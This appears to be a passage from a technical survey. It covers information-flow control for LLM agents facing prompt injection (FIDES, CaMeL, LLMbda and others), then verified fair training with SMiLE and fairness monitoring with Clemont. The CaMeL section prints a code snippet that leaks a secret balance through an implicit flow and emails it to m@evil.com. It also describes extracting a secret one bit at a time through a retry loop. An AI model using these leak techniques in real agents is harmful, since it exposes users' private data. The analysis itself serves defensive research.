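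The zero depends partly on how they assigned the labels. They marked a data field as untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's attacks used it. This tests the enforcement fairly, but someone who deploys an agent doesn't know in advance where attacks will appear.

The table shows the share of tasks completed when there was no attack, using OpenAI's o1 model.

| Planner | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
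|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic, no checks | 70% | 82% | 96% | 88% |
| Basic, with checks | 48% | 75% | 38% | 17% |
| FIDES, no checks | 78% | 75% | 79% | 79% |
| FIDES, with checks | 65% | 68% | 56% | 54% |

On average, FIDES with checks completed 61% of the tasks, compared with 84% for the unprotected planner. The 6.3% loss that Costa and colleagues also report is for FIDES with its checks off, when it has no guarantee. A better model would close part of the gap, but the policies block some tasks by design. Many banking tasks, for example, ask the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, which looks the same as an injection attack. Queries to the quarantined model also take extra time and tokens, but the paper gives no figures for this overhead.

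### What the labels guarantee

Costa and colleagues claim explicit secrecy rather than noninterference. They argue that noninterference would be too restrictive, since it would essentially forbid any tool that writes to a public place after any tool that reads a secret. Explicit secrecy requires that the steps an agent took in a given run, if repeated with any other secret data, have the same public effects. It ignores what an observer learns from which steps the agent took. For example, if an agent reads a medical file and opens a public web page only when a test was positive, anyone who can see the visits learns the result.

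The paper defines explicit secrecy formally but doesn't include a proof that the algorithm enforces it. The definition also misses some direct leaks, because it treats text that the planner has already read as part of the fixed steps. An agent that reads a balance of 100 and posts "100" on a public page satisfies the definition, because the fixed step "post 100" has the same effect whatever the balance was. The labels would block that post, so the system is stricter than its definition.

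CaMeL, which Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues published in 2025, is more flexible than FIDES. The planner writes a program, and an interpreter tracks which values depend on which, checking policies at each tool call. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, point out that it has no comparable soundness theorem, and they describe a leak of the following kind:

```
rich = True
tmp = True
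if balance > 1000: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

With a balance of 5,000, the third line sets tmp to False and labels it secret. The fourth line does nothing, so rich stays True with a public label, and the email goes out. With a balance of 500, the third line does nothing, tmp stays public, and the fourth line sets rich to False, so no email goes out. The recipient learns whether the balance is above 1,000, even though the interpreter assigned every public label according to its rules.

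The interpreter can't label an assignment that it never executes, because it tracks only one run and the leak is a difference between two. A standard fix is to stop the program when it tries to change a public variable under a secret condition, here at tmp = False. Whether the program stops still reveals one bit. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL's interpreter runs inside an ordinary retry loop that doesn't track labels, so an attacker can collect these bits one at a time. About 20 well-chosen attempts could find a balance of up to a million.

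### How sampling changes the definition

Language models usually sample their words at random, so noninterference for them has to be defined on output distributions instead of single outputs. For any two secrets, the same public input must give every public output the same probability.

Runs that a policy check stops complicate this, because they produce no output. Garby and colleagues therefore accept two distributions if some single distribution gives every output at least as much probability as either of them does. Suppose that with one secret the agent answers "yes" in 50% of runs and "no" in 40%, and a check stops the other 10%. With another secret, the figures are 60%, 30% and 10%. The larger figures for "yes" and "no" are 60% and 40%. They add up to 100%, so the stopped runs could account for the whole difference, and the definition accepts the pair. If the second secret gave 70%,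 20% and 10%, the larger figures would be 70% and 40%. The definition would reject that pair, because a distribution can't add up to 110%.

The average share of stopped runs also limits the leak. In the accepted example, the two distributions can differ by at most 10%, measured as half the sum of the absolute differences between their probabilities. If no run stops, the distributions must be identical. Like the one-bit leak above, this limit applies to each run.

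LLMbda is a small programming language for agents in which every value and the conversation itself carry a label. Garby and colleagues prove that every program in it satisfies their definition, including programs that run code written by the model. The theorem holds for any model whose responses depend only on the conversation it receives. Lean, a program that checks mathematical proofs, has verified the proof, and the verified interpreter is the one that calls the model.

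An agent built in LLMbda withstood all but two of 1,296 attacked runs on AgentDojo's banking tasks. It completed about as many tasks as CaMeL did with CaMeL's checks off, and turning those checks on halved CaMeL's success. The theorem guarantees that labels are correct, but the policies decide what labelled data may do, so an attack can still succeed. A program can also explicitly reclassify untrusted data as trusted. The theorem then still protects secrets but no longer protects against that data.

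### Exceptions and messages the model writes

Useful agents need such exceptions, and several systems from 2026 differ in who grants them. *APPA* (2026) lets an agent continue after a blocked call only if an authority the developers registered beforehand approves that exact call. The model can't change the list of authorities. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026) instead uses a separate language model to judge whether a message is unrelated to the protected records and may therefore leave. Its confidentiality theorem ensures that every message passes through this check, but the protection still depends on the model's judgement, which can be wrong.

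Another approach is to keep the secret out of the context, just as a developer can delete a secret column from a classifier's inputs. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (2026) gives the example of AirGapAgent, which limits the private data that enter a conversation. Withholding data prevents the model from revealing them, but also from using them.

*PACE* (2026) proves that a program's output doesn't depend on a secret if ordinary code produces the output and the model's choice of inputs to that code doesn't depend on the secret. A library call with arguments fixed by the code meets this condition, but an email that the model writes from a context containing the secret does not. Proving that the email doesn't depend on the secret would require proving noninterference for the model itself, which no current verifier can do for a network of its size.

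## Can these requirements be built in or watched at run time instead?

Verification often fails on large networks. When it succeeds, it often finds a counterexample pair, and the developer still has to repair the network. Monotone architectures and certified fair training each build in one requirement, and the labels around a language model control its tools, not the model itself. SMiLE, a training method from 2025, uses one design for several requirements. Another option is to leave the network unchanged and monitor its decisions after deployment.

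### A small part that limits a large one

Francobaldi, Lombardi and Lodi (2025), in *SMiLE*, build a network from four parts:

1. The main network, or backbone, h turns the input u into a short list of numbers, called the embedding. It can have any size and any activation function.
2. Two small bounding functions, low and high, compute a lower and an upper limit for each number in the embedding.
3. A clip operation moves any number outside its limits to the nearest limit.
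4. A linear function g, the head, turns the clipped list into the output.

Together they compute

f(u) = g( clip( h(u), low(u), high(u) ) ).

The head only receives numbers between low(u) and high(u), whatever the backbone computes, so a solver can ignore the backbone. It searches for two inputs u and u′ that meet the input condition, and embeddings z and z′ within their limits, for which g(z) and g(z′) break the requirement. If it proves that none exist, no pair of real runs can break the requirement. The guarantee is global because the search covers every input in the domain, not only the training data.

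Take the toy lender as the backbone, with a single number as the embedding and a head that returns it unchanged. Let the limits be

low(x, s) = x/2 − 0.1,  high(x, s) = x/2 + 0.1.

For the applicants (1, 0) and (1, 1), the backbone computes 0 and 1, and clipping changes these to 0.4 and 0.6. The limits do not depend on s, so for every x, flipping s moves the score by at most 0.2. The same proof would work for a backbone with a billion parameters. But the lender still refuses the first applicant and approves the second, because the cut-off of 0.5 lies between their scores.

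In the fairness experiments, the backbone has 64 ReLUs, so an ordinary product network would have 128. Each bounding function has 4, so the solver handles only 16 for both runs. However, the solver also considers embeddings that the backbone never produces, so it may reject a network that meets the requirement.

### Training until no pair remains

An earlier version of SMiLE handled only requirements on single runs and removed violations by adjusting the head. This fails for two runs. The solver can choose one embedding at the top of its limits and the other at the bottom, and if the limits are far apart, the head can bring the two outputs together only by becoming almost constant. The new version also adjusts the bounding functions, in three phases:

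1. **Pretraining.** The program fits the data with the backbone and with each bounding function separately, and penalises the backbone for leaving its limits. Without this phase, the lower limit tends to rise above the upper one, which blocks most of the training signal.
2. **Training.** The solver finds a pair that breaks the requirement, and the program adds the size of the violation to the training loss. The weight on this penalty grows for as long as the violation lasts. Once the program has fixed one pair, the solver looks for another.
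3. **Post-training.** The program ignores the data and changes the weights as little as it can to remove the remaining pairs, until the solver proves that there are none.

Because the head is linear, the worst embeddings always lie on their limits. The program records which limit each number lies on rather than its value. If it recorded the value, a tiny shift in the limits would count as a fix, and the solver would have to run again almost immediately.

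Training can use any violating pair, but only a complete search can show that none exists. The solver therefore starts with a short time limit and doubles it whenever it finds neither a pair nor a proof. If it reaches the maximum time in the last phase, it still gives an upper bound on the largest violation.

### Exact requirements leave the backbone no room

The solver chooses z and z′ independently, even when u and u′ are the same input. Two identical inputs meet the input conditions of monotonicity, global robustness and attribute-flip fairness. A proof of one of these requirements with tolerance ε therefore also shows that all embeddings within the limits for one input give outputs within ε of each other. This means the backbone can change the output by at most ε at any given input.

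In the example, the gap of 0.2 between the limits uses up the whole tolerance, so the limits themselves can't depend on s.

Monotonicity has no tolerance, so every embedding within the limits must give the same output. Apart from the solver's numerical tolerance, the finished network therefore computes g(low(u)), which depends on the head and the bounding functions but not on the backbone. In the monotonicity experiments, g(low(u)) is a network with a single hidden layer of 32 ReLUs, although the backbone has five hidden layers. The backbone may still help during training.

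### Accuracy and training time

Francobaldi and colleagues tested SMiLE on monotonicity by training a one-input network on each of nine curves of the form y = x + α sin(ωx). All but the mildest curve fall in places, so a monotone network can't fit them exactly. All nine networks were proved monotone. The test included no competing method, so it doesn't show how SMiLE compares with monotone architectures.

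For global robustness, the task was to recognise the digit zero among MNIST images. The network outputs a number, the logit, that is positive for "zero" and negative for "not zero". The logit must change by at most ε when every pixel changes by at most δ. The main competitor was CROWN-IBP, which penalises violations around each training image. The table gives accuracy on 1,000 test images, then the share of those images that the method both classified correctly and certified against every change of size δ. SMiLE's figures are averages over three values of ε.

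| δ | Ordinary training | CROWN-IBP | SMiLE |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0.01 | 99.6%, 0% | 100%, 99.9% | 98.8%, 97.6% |
| 0.05 | 99.6%, 0% | 99.7%, 99.2% | 97.9%, 94.3% |
| 0.10 | 99.6%, 0% | 99.6%, 99.0% | 95.9%, 90.6% |

SMiLE is less accurate in every row. About one MNIST digit in ten is a zero, so a network that always outputs "not zero" would be right about 90% of the time, and no attack could change its output. At δ = 0.1, SMiLE's certified accuracy is hardly better than that.

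SMiLE is faster, however. Training took 7,717 seconds on average, compared with 14,138 for CROWN-IBP, and classifying and certifying the test images took 0.03 seconds instead of 11.2. CROWN-IBP has to compute new bounds for every image, while a SMiLE network already has a limit that holds everywhere, so the system only has to check whether the logit is more than ε away from 0. If it isn't, the system gives the user a warning, much like the extra class of Leino and colleagues.

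For fairness, Francobaldi and colleagues compared SMiLE with CertiFair, Khedr and Shoukry's training framework, on the COMPAS dataset, a law-school dataset and a crime-rate dataset, with race as the protected attribute. SMiLE's networks were more accurate, and flipping race in the test data generally changed their outputs no more than it changed CertiFair's. Every SMiLE network also had a proof of fairness for the whole domain.

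These proofs guarantee less as ε grows. On the law-school data, ε ranged from 1 to 5, measured on the logit, which the sigmoid turns into a probability. A change of 5 in the logit can move a student's predicted chance from 8% to 92%. On COMPAS, the smallest ε was 0.2, which still allows a change from about 47.5% to 52.5%, enough to flip a decision at a 50% cut-off.

The method also has a narrower range than verification with auxiliary networks. The allowed change in the output must be a fixed number, so the method can't express a Lipschitz condition. Francobaldi and colleagues leave Lipschitz conditions and variable-length inputs such as text to future work.

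### Why a monitor has to remember

Monitoring needs no training and no access to the network's weights. *Monitoring Robustness and Individual Fairness* (Gupta, Henzinger and colleagues, 2025) presents Clemont, a tool that records a network's inputs and decisions and raises an alarm when two close inputs have received different decisions.

A monitor for equal approval rates needs only a few running counts, such as the number of applicants and approvals in each group. It can only estimate the true rates, because no finite set of decisions can prove that they differ. *Monitoring of Static Fairness* (2025) describes monitors that output a range for the fairness measure. With high probability, one version's range is correct at any given step, and a stricter version's ranges are correct at every step.

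A monitor can't check a two-run requirement from counts alone. If it deletes the record of a refused applicant and the lender then approves someone who is close to that person and to nobody else, the monitor misses the violation. Clemont therefore stores every input with its decision, which for a lender means a growing file of personal records.

For each new decision, it takes three steps:

1. Find all stored inputs within a distance ε of the new one.
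2. Report those that received a different decision.
3. Store the new input and its decision.

The report gives a person the cases to examine, but the monitor can't tell which of the two decisions was wrong.

### Finding close inputs quickly

The first step is a well-studied problem called fixed-radius nearest neighbour search. Clemont can use four methods for it.

Brute force compares the new input with every stored one, so the time grows in proportion to the number of stored inputs.

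A k-d tree repeatedly splits the input space in two, so a search can skip branches that are too far away. It works well when inputs have few features. Adding each new input to the tree would mean rebuilding it every time, so Clemont puts new inputs in a small buffer, searches the buffer by brute force, and rebuilds the tree only when the buffer is full.

A sorting method called SNN gives each input a single key. If two keys differ by more than ε, the inputs are also more than ε apart, so a search for inputs within ε of a given one only has to check those with nearby keys. This works for Euclidean distance, but not when distance is measured as the largest change in any one feature.

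The last method handles that distance by dividing each feature into intervals of width ε and recording which combinations of intervals have occurred. It stores them in a binary decision diagram, a compact way to represent a yes-or-no function. If ε is one year, the ages 34.1 and 35.9 fall in neighbouring intervals although they are 1.8 years apart. Clemont therefore checks the candidates from neighbouring intervals by brute force.

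If the distance between two inputs is the largest difference in any one feature, several processors can also share the search. Two inputs are then close exactly when they are close in every feature, so each processor can search a few features, and the true neighbours are the inputs that all the processors find.

### Time, memory and alarms

The conference version of *Monitoring Robustness and Individual Fairness* gives the average time per decision and the total memory for whole datasets:

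| Dataset | Inputs | Numbers per input | Brute force | k-d tree | Memory, brute force |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| COMPAS | 6,200 | 18 | 0.31 ms | 0.49 ms | 223 MB |
| Adult | 48,800 | 15 | 0.69 ms | 1.21 ms | 250 MB |
| CIFAR-10 | 20,000 | 3,100 | 3.71 ms | 6.09 ms | 2.2 GB |
| ImageNet | 10,000 | 150,500 | 0.26 s | 7.73 s | 64 GB |

Brute force was fastest almost everywhere because these sequences are short. Sixteen parallel threads cut the k-d tree's time on ImageNet to 0.62 seconds. In a longer test with 10.5 million records from particle physics, the decision diagrams were fastest when there were few features and ε was large. None of these times depend on the network's size. One of the CIFAR-10 networks has 366 million parameters, far more than verifiers for pairs of runs can handle.

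On COMPAS, the monitor raised an alarm for 55.4% of people with an ordinary network from the CertiFair study and for 40.6% with the version trained for fairness. On Adult, the figures were 23.2% and 2.5%. Not all of these alarms indicate discrimination. The monitor counted two people as similar if their features other than the protected attribute differed by up to 0.16. By the chain argument, any classifier that uses a continuous feature gives different decisions to some pair of similar people, even if it ignores the protected attribute.

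For image classifiers, training for robustness cut alarms to about a fifth on CIFAR-10 and a quarter on ImageNet, but barely reduced them on the related CIFAR-100. Gupta and colleagues deliberately altered some of the images in these sequences. An alarm requires two close images, so an attacker who sends only the altered version of a photograph would probably not trigger one.

In another test, they used a separate trained network to measure how far apart images were in content. Stronger distortions usually led to fewer alarms. They suspect the distorted images ended up too far from the originals to count as similar.

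In *FairMon*, Baumeister, Finkbeiner and colleagues cite earlier work suggesting that monitoring can in principle provide the human oversight that the EU's AI Act requires. They add that the available tools have critical shortcomings in areas such as credit lending.

### A pair the monitor misses

An alarm proves that the network breaks the global requirement, because the monitor has found a real counterexample pair. Silence covers only the inputs that the monitor has seen. Suppose that Clemont watches the toy lender and compares applicants with different s whose values of x are within 0.1 of each other. Five people apply:

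| Applicant (x, s) | Score | Decision | Similar earlier applicant |
|---|---|---|---|
| (0.3, 0) | 0 | refused | none |
| (1.2, 1) | 1 | approved | none |
| (0.7, 0) | 0 | refused | none |
| (0.35, 1) | 0.35 | refused | the first, also refused |
| (1.8, 1) | 1 | approved | none |

The monitor stays silent. A verifier would find the pair (1, 0) and (1, 1) before anyone applied.

If a sixth person with (1.25, 0) applies, the lender refuses her, and the monitor raises an alarm because the lender approved the second applicant. The lender can still hold back the refusal and have a person look at the case. If the two had applied in the opposite order, the alarm would have come only when the lender approved the other applicant, perhaps months after refusing her.

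The absence of alarms is weaker evidence of fairness when there are more features. If features are independent and spread evenly between 0 and 1, two random people are within 0.1 of each other on one feature with probability 0.19. The probability that they are this close on all of 10 features is about 6 in 100 million. The 48,800 people in Adult form about 1.2 billion pairs, so we would expect about 73 close ones. With 20 features, we would expect no close pairs and therefore no alarms, however unfair the network was. Real data are less evenly spread, so close pairs are more common, but people with unusual features may still have no neighbours.

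SMiLE's guarantee holds no matter who applies. If a SMiLE network has a proof that its score changes by at most ε, a monitor that checks the same limit on the scores can never raise an alarm, except because of rounding errors.

A lender that can run the network itself can check attribute-flip fairness by flipping s for each real applicant and comparing the two decisions, as mentioned earlier. It needs no stored records and doesn't have to wait for a similar applicant. In the example, this check would have revealed the problem at the second applicant, since the network approves (1.2, 1) but refuses (1.2, 0). Global robustness can't be checked this way, because the second input could be any point near the first.
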